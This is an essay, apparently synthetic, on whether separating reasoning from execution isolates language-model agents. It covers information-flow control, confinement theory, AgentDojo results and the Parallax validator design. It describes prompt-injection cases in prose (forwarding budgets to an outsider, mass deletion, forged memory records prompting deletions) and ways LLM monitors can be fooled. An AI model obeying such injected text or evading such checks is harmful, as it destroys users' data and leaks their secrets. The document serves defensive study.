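# Whether separating reasoning from execution isolates influence in language model agents

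## How an agent turns a model's text into actions

A language model agent is a software system in which a language model chooses steps towards a goal and an ordinary program, called the harness, carries them out. The model takes in text and returns text. When an agent deletes a file or sends a payment, the harness does so after reading what the model wrote. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (Joshi, 2026) starts from the same division: "A language model on its own only writes text."

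Some designers argue that if the part of an agent that reasons never executes anything, a builder can isolate it so that a misled model can do no harm. Computer scientists faced a similar problem in the 1970s with programs that handled other people's secrets, and they developed a theory of how information moves through a computation. Several agent designs from 2025 and 2026 borrow that theory. Whether this separation isolates anything depends on what still passes between the model and the harness.

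### One turn of the loop

Suppose a user asks about Friday's appointments. The harness builds a list of messages, each with a role. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the usual layout: a system message with the developer's standing instructions, a user message with the task, then assistant messages (what the model wrote) alternating with tool messages (what the tools returned). The harness adds a description of each tool the model may ask for, such as a `read_calendar` function that takes a date. It then serialises the whole list, which means flattening it into one string of tokens, the word fragments that models read and write.

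The model returns tokens whether it is writing prose or requesting a tool, and only the structure of the text distinguishes the two. If the reply is ordinary prose, the harness shows it to the user and stops. If the reply contains a tool call, the harness runs the requested function. Anthropic's *API usage primer for Claude* describes a typical procedure, in which the developer's code extracts the function name, an identifier and the input, runs the matching function, and sends the result back in a new message under the same identifier. The harness then calls the model again with the longer history, and the cycle repeats until a reply contains no tool call.

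*From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* (Zhu and Cai, 2026) traces this loop to three earlier systems. ReAct interleaved written reasoning with actions and observations. Toolformer taught a model when to call outside software and how to use the results. Reflexion kept written feedback from failed attempts so later attempts could improve without changing the model's weights.

The harness doesn't have to run what the model asks for. Joshi treats the model's reply as "a request, not a decision", but the simplest agents run every well-formed request. Safer designs add a check between parsing the call and running it, and they differ mainly in what information the check uses.

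### Encode, decode, execute

Mu, Shen and Shu (2026), in *Your Policy Is Secretly a Harness*, reduce a harness to three functions. One encodes the current state into a context for the model, another decodes the model's reply into an action, and the last executes that action. With the model in its place, a turn looks like this:

```
context = encode(state)
reply   = model(context)
action  = decode(reply)
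state   = execute(action, state)
```

"State" covers both what the harness tracks, including tool results and the remaining budget, and the outside world that the tools interact with. The model supplies one of the four lines.

Different replies can decode to the same action. A JSON object and a function-call string, for instance, may issue the same database query. The probability that the agent takes action *a* in state *s* is therefore a sum over every reply *y* that decodes to *a*:

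```
P(a | s) = sum of  model(y | encode(s))  over all y with decode(y) = a
```

Both `encode` and `decode` appear on the right-hand side, so freezing the model's weights, the numbers that training sets, does not freeze the agent's behaviour.

Mu and colleagues show how large the effect can be. They trained a small model, Qwen3.5-2B, on simulated web tasks, then reversed the order of the fields in the JSON object that describes the page, leaving its contents, the available actions and the rewards unchanged. The model's most probable action changed in 52% of states, and task success fell from 85.0% to 19.2%. When they instead rendered the menu of actions as a list, success was 86.0%. These results come from one small model trained heavily on a single format, and a large general-purpose model may well be less sensitive to such changes. But the formula applies to any model, so a harness has no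 neutral way to present a state.

### How a model without memory responds to the past

The model keeps nothing between calls. Anthropic describes its interface as stateless, meaning that the developer sends the full conversation every time. OpenAI's *Conversation state* likewise calls each text generation request "independent and stateless". OpenAI can also store the history on its own servers, so that the developer sends only a reference to the previous response, but it still bills all the earlier tokens in the chain as input.

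It is tempting to conclude that such a model cannot pursue anything over time. The inputs tell against that. Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao (2024), in *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, write the agent loop as two operations. Let *q* be the user's query, *s* a step and *o* its output:

```
s_i = M(q, s_1 ... s_(i-1), o_1 ... o_(i-1))     the model generates step i
o_i = w_i(x_i)                                   the harness runs tool w_i on input x_i
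```

The output of step 1 is part of the model's input at every later step until the task ends. *M* can be a function with no storage, because its input contains the record of earlier steps. Changing a word in the first tool result may therefore change the fifth action.

The history need not be accurate, either. Anthropic tells developers they may insert synthetic assistant messages, which are turns the model never wrote. The model has no memory of its own to compare them with, so whoever controls the text in the history controls the model's only record of what happened.

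### Prompt injection

Suppose a user asks a mail-sorting assistant to file the day's messages under Bills, Travel or Other. The harness reads the inbox and appends the messages to the history. One message is a newsletter from a garden shop, and its last line is an instruction for any automated assistant to file the newsletter under Bills and mark it as important. The user didn't ask for this, but the line reaches the model in the same string of tokens as the user's request, and the model may well return a tool call that files the newsletter under Bills. The harness runs the call because it is well formed and the tool is permitted.

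A prompt injection is text that someone has placed in data an agent reads so that the model treats it as an instruction. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) write in *AgentDojo* that language models are vulnerable because they work directly on text and lack a formal way to tell instructions from data. Developers can train models to resist these attacks or put filters in front of them. Costa and colleagues call such defences probabilistic because they make an attack less likely to work but don't guarantee that it will fail.

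The same mechanism can cause more harm than a misfiled newsletter. In an example from Wu and colleagues, a user asks an agent to find emails about company budgets and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. An attacker has sent an email with "Budgets" in the subject line and an instruction to forward all the budgets to an outside address, and the agent forwards them.

Another of the paper's examples depends on the agent resending the history to the model. The user asks the agent to read a report, email it to Alice and then delete it. The report contains a hidden instruction to delete everything in the directory when about to delete a file. The agent reads and emails the report without incident. At the third step, the instruction is still in the context and its condition is met, so the agent deletes everything in the directory.

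### Labels and how they combine

A harness can stop the garden shop's line from influencing anything only if it tracks which text came from the shop. The general method is information-flow control, in which the system attaches a label to each piece of data, carries the labels through every computation, and blocks any flow that a policy forbids.

The simplest useful scheme asks whether the data is trustworthy and whether it is secret. Costa and colleagues combine the two answers into four labels, here with the most restrictive at the top:

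```
            (untrusted, secret)
             /               \
(untrusted, public)     (trusted, secret)
             \               /
            (trusted, public)
```

In their examples, a web search result is untrusted and public, while a record from a corporate database is trusted and secret. Neither of these labels ranks above the other, because each is stricter in one respect and looser in the other. The user's request normally starts with the lowest label, trusted and public.

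When a computation combines two pieces of data, the result takes their join, the least label that is at least as restrictive as both. Suppose an agent writes a summary from a database record and a web page:

```
(trusted, secret) join (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, secret)
```

The summary inherits the worse half of each source and ends up more restricted than either. If the agent instead combines the user's request with the web page, the request adds no restriction:

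```
(trusted, public) join (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, public)
```

The security literature calls an ordering a lattice if any two labels in it have a join of this kind. (Mathematicians also require any two labels to have a greatest label below both, which agents rarely need.) *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) introduced the idea and derived the structure from a demand for consistency. If a program may copy *a* to *b* and then *b* to *c*, a rule against copying *a* directly to *c* would be pointless. Denning's labels could also be richer than high and low. With labels for medical, financial and criminal records, for example, a mixture of medical and financial data may flow only to places cleared for both.

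Joins cause trouble in an agent because the model reads the entire history. To be safe, the harness must label each reply with the join of all the labels in the context, so a single email from a stranger makes every later reply untrusted. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003), in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, describe the same problem in older systems as label creep, in which labels keep rising during a run until the system treats most results as too sensitive for their intended use. Much of the engineering in FIDES, Costa and colleagues' agent, goes into slowing label creep.

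The other remedy is to lower a label on purpose. Declassification treats secret data as public, for example when its owner decides to let others read it. Endorsement treats untrusted data as trusted. Li, Mao and Zdancewic's *Information Integrity Policies* gives the example of a program that has checked a digital signature on data from the network. Both are deliberate exceptions to the policy, so the guarantee depends on good judgement about when to make them.

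### Confidentiality and integrity as mirror images

According to Li and colleagues, a confidentiality policy restricts who can read data and where it flows in the future, while an integrity policy restricts who can write data and what it derives from in the past. Confidentiality requires that secrets not reach public outputs, and integrity similarly requires that untrusted data not reach trusted outputs. Sabelfeld and Myers credit Biba with observing this parallel, which is useful because one mechanism can enforce both kinds of policy.

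The reflection is easy to see when labels are sets. Costa and colleagues take one document that A, B and C may read and another that B, C and D may read. Only B and C may read a text that draws on both, so the join is an intersection. If the same sets instead list the people who could have written each document, any of the four could have influenced the combined text, so the join is a union.

The budget attack first breaches integrity, when a stranger's text determines the recipient, and then confidentiality, when the figures leave the company.

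Integrity does not mirror confidentiality perfectly, though. As Sabelfeld and Myers point out, a system can damage integrity without any outside contact, by computing something incorrectly. An agent that misreads a trustworthy calendar and books the wrong Friday has not violated any label, because labels track influence, not correctness.

### Explicit and implicit flows

An explicit flow passes data by copying it or computing on it:

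```
salary = read_secret()
public = salary + 1
```

An implicit flow passes data through the choice of what to do. In this program, adapted from Portland State University's *Information-flow Security*, `secret` is either true or false:

```
public = False
if secret: public = True
```

The program never copies `secret` anywhere, but `public` ends up with the same value. Denning's example, "if *a* = 0, then set *b* to *c*", contains both kinds of flow in one statement. Data flows explicitly from *c* to *b* when the assignment runs. Data also flows implicitly from *a* to *b* whether or not the assignment runs, because an observer who sees that *b* has kept its old value can often infer that *a* was not zero.

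An action that does not happen can therefore carry information. This is hard to detect with a tool that monitors a program as it runs, because the tool records only the path the program takes. Sabelfeld and Myers argue that confidentiality is a property of all the paths a program could take. Taint tracking, the popular, low-overhead form of information-flow control, mostly follows data through copies and computations. In *Language-Based Security*, Chong (2024) writes that taint analysis differs from a fuller analysis mainly because it misses implicit flows, which the fuller analysis tracks by also labeling the program's current branch.

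Both explicit and implicit flows occur in ordinary agent work. If the agent pastes the text of an email into a chat message, the flow is explicit. If the user asks for a calendar event whenever someone proposes a meeting, the flow is implicit, because whether the agent creates an event depends on what a stranger wrote, even if the harness fills in every field from trusted sources. The distinction does not apply inside the model, which has no branches for an analyst to label, so a harness can treat the model only as a single operation on everything in its context.

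### Noninterference

The strictest promise in this field is noninterference: changing the protected inputs changes nothing that a given observer can see. It calls for a comparison of two runs. Li and colleagues consider a program *f* that takes a secret input and a public input, and returns a secret output and a public output. The program is noninterfering if, for all secrets *a* and *a′*,

```
f(a, b) = (c, d)   implies   f(a′, b) = (c′, d)
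```

If a program runs twice with the same public input *b* but different secret inputs, *a* and *a′*, its secret output may change from *c* to *c′*, but its public output must be *d* both times. Replacing "secret" with "tainted" and "public" with "untainted" gives the definition of integrity.

In the mail sorter, the protected input is the newsletter and the visible output is the list of tool calls. If the agent files the newsletter in one folder with the shop's last line in place and in another without it, the line interfered. But sorting mail requires the folder to depend on what each message contains, so full noninterference would rule out the task along with the attack.

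Designers respond by protecting less of the system. Wu and colleagues adapt the definition of noninterference to cover only the plan, which is the sequence of steps the agent generates. An attacker cannot alter those steps but may still corrupt the data that passes through them. This guarantee is real but much narrower than the word "noninterference" might suggest.

Whether a program is secure also depends on what the observer can see. Sabelfeld and Myers list running time, power consumption and whether the program ever halts among the channels through which a program can leak information, so a program may be secure against someone who reads its output but not against someone who times it. Language models usually sample their tokens at random, so two runs can also differ when the input is the same. One can compare the probabilities of the outputs instead, or assume that the model is deterministic,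 as Costa and colleagues do in their proof.

### Measuring attacks with AgentDojo

Proofs cover a model of an agent. To test working agents, many researchers use AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024. It simulates four settings, each with its own tools and made-up data: an office workspace with email, calendar and files, a Slack chat, a travel agency and a bank. It has 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill stored in a file. It also has injected tasks, which are an attacker's goals, such as sending money to the attacker's account. The benchmark plants the attack text in data that the agent will read, and pairs every user task with every injected task in the same setting.

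| Setting | User tasks | Injected tasks (2024) | Pairs (2024) | Pairs (version 1.2.1) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 40 | 6 | 240 | 560 |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 | 144 |
| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 | 949 |

The counts for version 1.2.1 come from *SecOPD* (2026), a paper on training models to withstand injections. All of the growth is in Workspace. At least part of it comes from *agentdojo inspect*, a modified copy in the US government's data catalogue. That copy added Workspace attacks on bulk data, which the main project later adopted. Totals from papers that used different versions are therefore not directly comparable.

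Each task has an ordinary code function that checks the agent's answer and the state of the simulated world before and after the run, then returns pass or fail. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that hijacks the agent might hijack the judge too. They report three numbers. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when nobody attacks. Utility under attack is the share of pairs in which it completes the user's task without adversarial side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of pairs in which the attacker's goal is achieved. *SecOPD* scores the user's success and the attacker's success separately, so a single run can count towards both.

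The 2024 scores are out of date. Every model then solved less than 66% of the user tasks, even without an attack. *AutoDojo* (2026), a successor that generates attacks tailored to the target, reports that DeepSeek-v4-Pro completes 89.5% of user tasks and that the standard fixed attack succeeds less than 10% of the time against it, even with no defence. Adding PIGuard, an injection detector, cut the fixed attack's success rate to 0.0%, but it also cut the share of user tasks completed without an attack to 54.4%. With PIGuard in place, the generated attacks still succeeded 8.2% of the time overall and 13.2% in the banking setting. Both rates are higher than the fixed attack achieved on the undefended model, so a low success rate for the fixed attack is weak evidence of safety.

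*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026), a survey, similarly criticises the field's benchmarks for using tasks so simple that a defence can score well through blunt refusals, without ever handling a task in which the right action depends on what a tool returned. The pass-or-fail checks can also be wrong. Costa and colleagues reviewed the 160 attacks that AgentDojo had marked as successful against their undefended agent and accepted 152 of them. In other runs, the benchmark counted attacks as successes even though a policy had stopped the tool from running.

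An attack's chance of success also depends on how much the user's request leaves open. *AutoDojo* sorts user tasks by how fully the request specifies what the agent should do. On the banking tasks, with Gemini 2.5 Flash and no defence, its attacks succeeded 66.7% of the time when the request left the choice of action open and 13.9% of the time when the request fully specified the action. With an open request, the agent has to take its next action from the data, where the attacker's text is placed.

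## Whether a program with no memory that only returns text can act

Because the harness does all the executing, the model has no side effects in the programming sense, and it keeps nothing between calls. On this view, a hijacked model poses little danger, because it can return the words "delete the files" any number of times without deleting anything.

The picture supports an argument with two premises and a conclusion:

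1. No privileges: the model cannot run a tool, open a file or spend money.
2. No state: the model keeps nothing from one call to the next.
3. No influence: therefore nothing the model reads or writes can change what happens in the world.

Recent writing on agents states both premises, that a language model only produces text and that it has no memory. The blog post *Agent harness* says that the bare model "can generate text, but it cannot act." The software company Modular says that models cannot run tools, execute code or retain state without a surrounding application. Zhu and Cai write that a model can reason well and still "possess no authority to act". *Position* (Perrier and Bennett, 2025) says that language models store no lasting record of prompts and outputs, and *Code as Agent Harness* (Fu, Wei and colleagues, 2026) describes the harness as "turning a stateless model into a functional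 agent".

Both premises, that the model has no memory and that it only returns text, are true of an ordinary model behind an ordinary interface. Most of these writers use them only to explain why an agent needs a harness. Concluding that the model has no influence requires a further inference. Whether that inference is sound matters for designs such as Parallax, which puts reasoning and execution in separate processes.

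### Lampson's confinement problem

The question is older than language models. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) considered a customer who wants to run someone else's program, the "service", on confidential data. Access controls can keep the service out of the customer's other files, but the customer still has to give it data to work on, and the service may pass that data to its owner. Confinement means preventing the service from transmitting information to any program except its caller.

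Lampson listed ways a service can leak data to its owner. A service with memory can collect the data and hand it over the next time its owner calls. It can write to a file in the owner's directory or send the owner's program a message. It can also send the data one bit at a time by opening and closing a shared file while the owner's program keeps testing whether the file is in use. Or it can alternate between heavy calculation and heavy disk use, and the owner can read the pattern from the speed of the machine.

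The first rule Lampson drew from this list is the "no state" premise. A confined program "must be memoryless", meaning it keeps nothing inside itself between calls. Lampson thought this easy to arrange and spent the rest of the note on programs without memory. Total isolation, which forbids such a program to call any other, would be enough to confine it, but Lampson rejected this rule as impractical because even ordinary requests to the operating system count as calls. A looser rule lets the program call others if each is either trusted or also confined.

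The service can leak data by encoding it in the bill, which is hard to prevent because the service's owner must get a copy. Restricting the form of bills reduces the leak to "a few bits or tens of bits". To reduce it to zero, the customer has to determine the bill in advance, as a company does with a purchase order, and the service must be limited to accepting or rejecting the job.

The harness cannot forbid tool calls, since the agent exists to make them, but their contents can depend on anything the model has read. The harness could keep untrusted text from influencing the calls by settling every call before the model sees any of that text.

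A language model also differs from Lampson's service in a way that further weakens the isolation argument. Lampson's definition lets the service tell its caller, the customer, anything, because the data was the customer's to begin with. A language model's caller is the harness, the program that acts. A model could therefore satisfy all of Lampson's rules and still determine who gets paid.

A misled model fits better under another injury that Lampson mentions but sets aside, in which the service does not perform as advertised. He saw no general technical remedy for this short of certifying the program. Incorrect outputs at least give the customer evidence for a claim, but an agent's harness may act on them before anyone has looked at them.

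Two years later, Saltzer and Schroeder defined confinement and complete isolation separately in the glossary of *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. Confinement lets a borrowed program use data but not release it. Complete isolation divides a system into compartments with no flow of information or control between them. A model whose replies select tool calls may be confined, but it is not completely isolated.

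### Fenton's memoryless subsystems

*Memoryless Subsystems* (Fenton, 1974) uses "memoryless" in a stronger sense, for a system that cannot communicate unauthorised information about its input to the outside world. Fenton derived a model of such a system and proved the model correct.

In a later textbook, Denning explains the machine that Fenton studied. It has three instructions: add one to a register (a numbered storage cell); subtract one from a register, or jump if it holds zero; and halt. Every register carries a label, and so does the machine's current place in the program. When the program branches on a secret register, that place takes on the secret label, which is how the machine tracks implicit flows. Until the program returns from the branch, the machine skips any instruction that would change a register with a lower label. The program may halt only after it has returned from every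 branch.

The machine must also skip those instructions silently. If it stopped with an error message, anyone who saw the message would learn which branch the program had taken. So the program runs on as though nothing had happened, which protects the secret but makes the program's mistakes hard to find. (What a branch can reveal when the program does not take it is a further difficulty.)

A language model stores nothing between calls, which makes it memoryless in Lampson's sense. Its reply can still depend on every word of the input, so it is not memoryless in Fenton's sense. Fenton's guarantee came from controlling how outputs derive from inputs, and a lack of storage does not provide that control.

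### From what the model reads to what the harness does

The argument against the third claim needs only two functions. Let *M* be the model and *H* the harness:

```
y = M(x)     the model reads x and returns the reply y
a = H(y)     the harness reads y and runs the action a
```

Take two inputs, *x* and *x′*, that differ only in a line a stranger wrote.

1. Suppose the model's replies to them differ, so that M(x) ≠ M(x′).
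2. Suppose the harness runs different actions for those two replies, so that H(M(x)) ≠ H(M(x′)).
3. Then changing the stranger's line, with all else fixed, changes the action. That is what it means for the line to influence the action.

These steps don't depend on who holds the passwords or on whether *M* stores anything, so both premises can be true while the conclusion is false. The same argument applies if the model samples its replies at random, except that the line then has influence if it makes some action more or less likely.

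The second step must concern the same two replies as the first. The input may change the reply in ways that don't affect the action, even if other changes to the reply would. In the mail sorter, the garden shop's line might change only how politely the model words its reply. The harness reads only the folder name, so the newsletter goes to the same place either way.

The stranger's line therefore has no influence if the harness ignores the model's text, maps every reply to the same action, or discards every part of the reply that the line can change. A backup that runs at midnight whatever the model writes is one example. An agent that worked entirely this way would have no use for a model. But a designer can block influence over part of an action, for example by taking a message's recipient from the user's request and leaving only the wording to the model. The stranger may still influence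 what the message says, but not who receives it.

The "no state" premise also fails over several steps, because the harness resends the history with every call, even though the model itself remains stateless, as Perrier and Bennett note. Notes and files outside the model can keep text for even longer.

A defender of the argument may reply that the harness is still what acts, which is a fair use of the word. Zhu and Cai treat agency as a property of the whole configured system, in which the model proposes, the harness mediates and the environment changes. But the user's files are gone whichever component is said to have acted. Security researchers call a program a confused deputy when it holds real authority and uses it for someone who has none. The harness can be a confused deputy because the model has no privileges of its own.

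### Counting the influence

Information theory puts a ceiling on how much a model can convey through its actions. Suppose that at each step an agent picks one of 8 tools and one of 100 recipients, and that the harness fixes everything else. Each step has 8 × 100 = 800 possible outcomes, and a choice among *N* outcomes carries at most log2(*N*) bits:

```
one step:     log2(800)        =  about 9.6 bits
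20 steps:     20 × log2(800)   =  about 193 bits
```

An attacker reaches the ceiling only if they can steer the agent to any of the 800 outcomes at will. An attack that works half the time conveys less information. But the ceiling covers only the choices of tool and recipient. If the model also writes a 200-token message from a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, the message alone can carry up to 3,322 bits, far more than all 20 choices of tool and recipient together.

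Lampson suggested limiting capacity in this way as a cheaper alternative for customers who could accept some leakage. The limit protects long secrets well. An agent restricted to those choices can send at most 193 bits in 20 steps, so it cannot reveal the whole of a random 256-bit encryption key in that time.

We can infer much less from the limit about harmful actions. Suppose the harness fixes the payee and the amount of a $50,000 invoice, and asks the model only whether to pay. The reply carries at most one bit, but it decides whether $50,000 leaves the account. Bits measure how many alternatives there are, not what depends on them. Denning notes that a single leaked bit may matter a great deal if it is, for instance, "a signal to attack".

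One bit can confirm a correct guess of a long secret. Denning describes a program that compares every secret variable in a system with a guessed value and finishes without an error only if all the guesses are right. Whether the program finishes normally is one bit of information, but a normal finish confirms every value.

### An experiment with forged memory records

The composition argument shows that influence is possible, but not how often real models allow it. Leong (2026) measured this in *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* for agents that must decide for themselves which of several conflicting instructions to follow. Leong published the paper in August 2026 and revised it in October, telling readers not to cite the first version for its headline results. The figures here come from the revision.

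The main experiment gave an agent a stored memory and a tool for deleting files in a simulated file system. One memory record told the agent to preserve a project directory. Another, which Leong had forged, claimed some authority and called for a clean-up. The system prompt told the agent to consult its memory and did not forbid deletion. Leong wrote 50 versions of the forged record and tried each one ten times on each of 29 endpoints, which are named models reached through an institution's gateway, producing 14,294 valid trials. In the baseline trials, the memory returned a message that it held no clean-up policies.

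The result depends heavily on what counts as a deletion:

| What counts | Mean over 29 endpoints | 95% interval | Baseline, all trials pooled |
|---|---|---|---|
| A delete call that names the protected directory | 1.21% | 0.5–2.1% | 0.07% |
| Also a call on a folder that contains it | 12.9% | 6.6–20.1% | 0.08% |
| Any delete call | 20.2% | 11.4–29.9% | 0.75% |

The middle rule seems closer to what matters here than the narrowest one, although Leong fixed the narrowest before collecting the data and chose the middle one after seeing them, which would normally be a reason to prefer the narrowest. None of the 50 forged records named a directory, so the model had to choose one, and it usually chose the parent folder. Deleting that folder and its contents would also destroy the protected directory. Under any of the three rules, the rate with the forged record is many times the baseline.

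That comparison changes two things at once, because the baseline has neither a forged claim of authority nor a request to delete. In a smaller control experiment, Leong gave three models a read-only system prompt and had the user ask for the deletion every time, so that only the memory record differed. When the record claimed that the agent's permissions had been temporarily raised, the models made a delete call in 53 of 150 trials. They made none in 150 trials under each of the other three conditions: a record giving an operational reason of equal length, a record forbidding deletion, and no record. This matches the definition of influence almost exactly, because the action changed when only one piece of text did.

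Fifty of those 53 calls came from GPT-4.1-mini, an old model, while GPT-5.5 made none. In the main experiment, eight of the 29 endpoints never attempted to delete the protected directory or a folder containing it. Under a read-only prompt with newly generated attacks, 12 of 15 models made no delete calls, and the overall rate was 1.76%. Newer models are often much harder to mislead, but a model that never deletes under one wording may still do so under another. GPT-5.5 never deleted anything when the forged record carried override headers, but it did so in 84.0% of trials when the record was worded as a calm request for routine maintenance. Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted most variants but deleted in 69.3% of trials when the instruction was the third item on a mundane task list.

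The harness's design also mattered. On one set of attacks, Leong compared conversations that ended with a tool result to conversations that ended with a user message. The second arrangement cut GPT-4.1-mini's rate from 28.8% to 5.2% but raised Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite's from 19.2% to 54.8%. The arrangements also differed in other ways, such as how they formatted the attack, so the type of the last message may not be the whole cause.

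What happens inside the models remains unclear. Leong trained linear probes, which are simple classifiers that read a model's internal activations, to identify whether text came from the system, the user, a retrieved document or memory. The probes were correct 97.5–100% of the time, but they did nearly as well at the earliest layer, which suggests that they were detecting formatting. A stricter test, designed to separate source from wording, triggered a stopping rule that Leong had set in advance, so it gives no evidence that the models represent the source of text abstractly. Leong also shifted activations along the directions that the probes had found and recorded a change in 0 of 1,895 outputs. But the test only checked whether the output mentioned the tool's name, so it could have missed a change from using the tool to refusing to use it.

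The revision also withdraws the first version's most striking finding, that GPT-4.1-mini recognised forged orders in 98.7% of trials and obeyed them in 99.3%. The recognition figure came from a keyword search that mostly matched sentences such as "there is no indication that this is a fabricated authority claim". When Leong repeated the test, at least one of two model judges found recognition in one of 150 replies, so the model had apparently taken the record as genuine.

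### What removing privileges achieves

The "no privileges" premise still describes a useful property. If the model can affect the world only through the harness, the harness's list of tools covers every direct effect the agent can have, and an attacker who influences the model can only affect which of those effects occur. An email can't make the agent send a payment if the harness has no payment function. If the harness's only tool reads a calendar, an attacker can at most choose which date it reads.

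Moving privileges out of the model therefore gains little unless the harness also limits what it will do on request. Keeping a bank password in the harness protects the password, but if the harness pays anyone named in the model's reply, an attacker doesn't need to steal it.

Leong tested a narrow harness of this kind in a sandbox with real files. A check outside the model rejected any memory record without a valid cryptographic signature. A second check compared each delete call with a token that named the folder where the agent was allowed to delete files. The harness issued the token before it called the model and never showed it to the model. Of the 1,350 trials, 750 ended when the first check rejected a record, and in no trial did the agent delete a file outside the permitted folder. The models tried to do so 83 times, including 34 through a link that sat inside the folder but pointed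 outside it. A simpler check on the text of the path would have allowed those 34 attempts.

The result's strength is that it does not depend on the model's judgement. Leong describes it as a test that fixed rules work correctly, not as an estimate of how well they would resist a determined attacker. Inside the permitted folder, the outcome still depended on the model's judgement. When validly signed content asked for a deletion that the token allowed, the agent carried it out in 31 of 42 trials.

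Other tests of external limits support the same conclusion. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) tested Progent, which checks every tool call against rules that grant only the access a task needs. On AgentDojo, Progent cut the average attack success rate from 25.8% to 4.2%, and an attack tailored to the defence did no better, succeeding 2.6% of the time. This is modest evidence, because the agent used a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, and the tailored attack used only one template.

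They contrast fixed rules with a model's trained resistance, which can wear down under repeated attempts. Attacks on an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.5, succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. A fixed rule returns the same result for the same call every time.

### Text that acts through its reader

If the designer removes every tool, the model's text goes only to a person, and the composition argument still applies with the person in the place of *H*. For example, a user pastes in a supplier's invoice and asks whether the new bank details look genuine. The invoice contains a hidden instruction for AI assistants to confirm them. The model replies that the details match the supplier's records, and the user pays.

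Narisetty and colleagues separate these cases from the ones their defences address. They call harmful text from a chatbot a content failure and a harmful action by an agent an authorization failure. This distinction helps in deciding what a check on tool calls can be expected to stop. But the model's influence extends beyond the actions it takes, so Zhu and Cai start their scale of delegated authority at recommendation, below any action the system takes itself.

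People carry out a model's output less predictably than a harness does, because they can doubt an answer, call the supplier or forget to act. But an agent's tool list doesn't restrict what its user can do, so removing the agent's payment function doesn't stop the user from making the payment. Requiring human approval before each action also gives only limited protection if the person relies on the model's account of what the action will do.

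That account can be badly wrong. Leong had two model judges read what the agents wrote in 1,647 of the trials in which the agents asked to delete a folder containing the protected directory. In 62.1% of these trials, both judges found that the text reported a deletion and said or implied that the protected directory had survived. On a real file system, deleting the folder with its contents would have destroyed the directory, and a user who trusted the report would have had no reason to check.

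## Parallax: reasoning and execution in separate processes

*PARALLAX: Why AI Agents That Think Must Never Act* (Fokou, April 2026) states the separation thesis most plainly: "The system that reasons about actions must be structurally unable to execute them." The part that executes actions must also be unable to reason about them, and an independent validator checks every request that passes from one to the other.

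Fokou argues that the usual alternative, putting safety instructions in the prompt, is inadequate because the instructions sit in the same context as the attack and fail once the model does. There is evidence that such instructions are weak even when the context contains no attacker's text. In *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, Jing (2026) told three models to require explicit approval before any dangerous action, and they still permitted 78.1% of the dangerous operations.

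### Two processes and a validator

OpenParallax, Fokou's open-source implementation, splits the harness into an agent process and an engine process. The agent process keeps the conversation, calls the model and forwards the model's tool calls to the engine, which holds the tools and the validator. The agent process cannot open files or run commands, and it can communicate only with the model provider's interface and the engine. At startup it attempts several forbidden operations, such as writing a file to the user's disk, and the program does not run if any succeeds. Fokou lists the design's complete dependence on the engine among its limits, because an attacker who compromises the engine can defeat all the other protections.

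The validator, called Shield, works in tiers. Fixed code first protects the system's own settings and logs, and an error at any tier blocks the action.

- Tier 0 compares the type of action and the file path with written rules, which allow the action, deny it or send it to a later tier.
- Tier 1 runs 37 pattern-matching rules alongside a small trained classifier, and either can block.
- Tier 2 asks a separate language model for a verdict, by default at most 100 times a day.
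- Tier 3 asks the user and treats five minutes of silence as a refusal.

Tier 2 fits poorly with the rule that the executing side cannot reason, because the engine itself calls this second model, the evaluator. Fokou limits the risk by giving the evaluator only the action's type and contents, without the conversation or a task description. The contents may still include an attacker's words, so the evaluator must also copy a secret token into its answer, and the engine blocks the action if the token is missing. This catches an evaluator that has abandoned its instructions altogether, but one that the attacker's text has persuaded to approve the action can still copy the token. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper, objects more generally to using language models as monitors, because nobody can state precisely which actions such a monitor will allow.

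The model also starts with a single tool, which only loads groups of other tools. Fokou presents this as a way to limit what a misled model can request. But the main agent chooses which groups to load, and Shield does not check that choice. The restriction therefore seems much stronger for sub-agents, which receive a fixed set of tools.

### Secrecy labels and rollback

The engine labels data by secrecy when it reads it. Fokou's paper defines four levels, from public to restricted, and the released software adds a fifth for credentials. No label records that a stranger wrote a piece of text, so the system can enforce a confidentiality policy but has no basis for an integrity policy.

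Even for secrecy, the labels are coarse. OpenParallax's *Information Flow Control* describes rules that classify a file by its path, so a file with "patient" in its name counts as restricted. Fokou acknowledges that sensitive content outside the rules will not get the right label. The flow check also allows any action type its policy doesn't list, so that new tools work without an update.

Following a secret through the model is harder than labelling a file. Fokou's main example of why labels matter is an agent that reads credentials, puts them in a web address and then requests that address. According to OpenParallax's *Changelog*, an agent in the first public release could similarly read a file of credentials and then send an email, because the email had no file path for the check to use. The next version records the highest sensitivity level seen in a session and checks later emails and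 web requests against it. This level is a join over everything the agent has read, so it causes label creep. After the agent reads one credential file, the policy can block every email for the rest of the session, including those that contain no secret.

Rollback is for harmful actions that get through. Before the engine overwrites or deletes a file, a component called Chronicle saves a copy, which the user can restore with a command. By default it keeps 100 copies for up to 30 days, so someone has to notice the damage while the copy still exists. Chronicle can't retract a sent email or reverse a request to an outside service, so Fokou recommends human approval for irreversible external actions.

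### One deletion, step by step

Suppose Ana asks her agent to delete the drafts that a shared notes file lists as out of date. A stranger with access to the notes has added `plan-b.md`, which Ana still needs. The model reads the list and returns a call to delete `/home/ana/project/plan-b.md`. The developer documentation for OpenParallax gives the order of the engine's checks, and with the paper's default settings the call would go roughly like this:

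1. The engine gives the request an identifier and computes a hash, a short fingerprint of its contents.
2. It classifies the file path. No rule matches `plan-b.md`, so the label is public.
3. The fixed protection check passes, because the file isn't one of the system's own.
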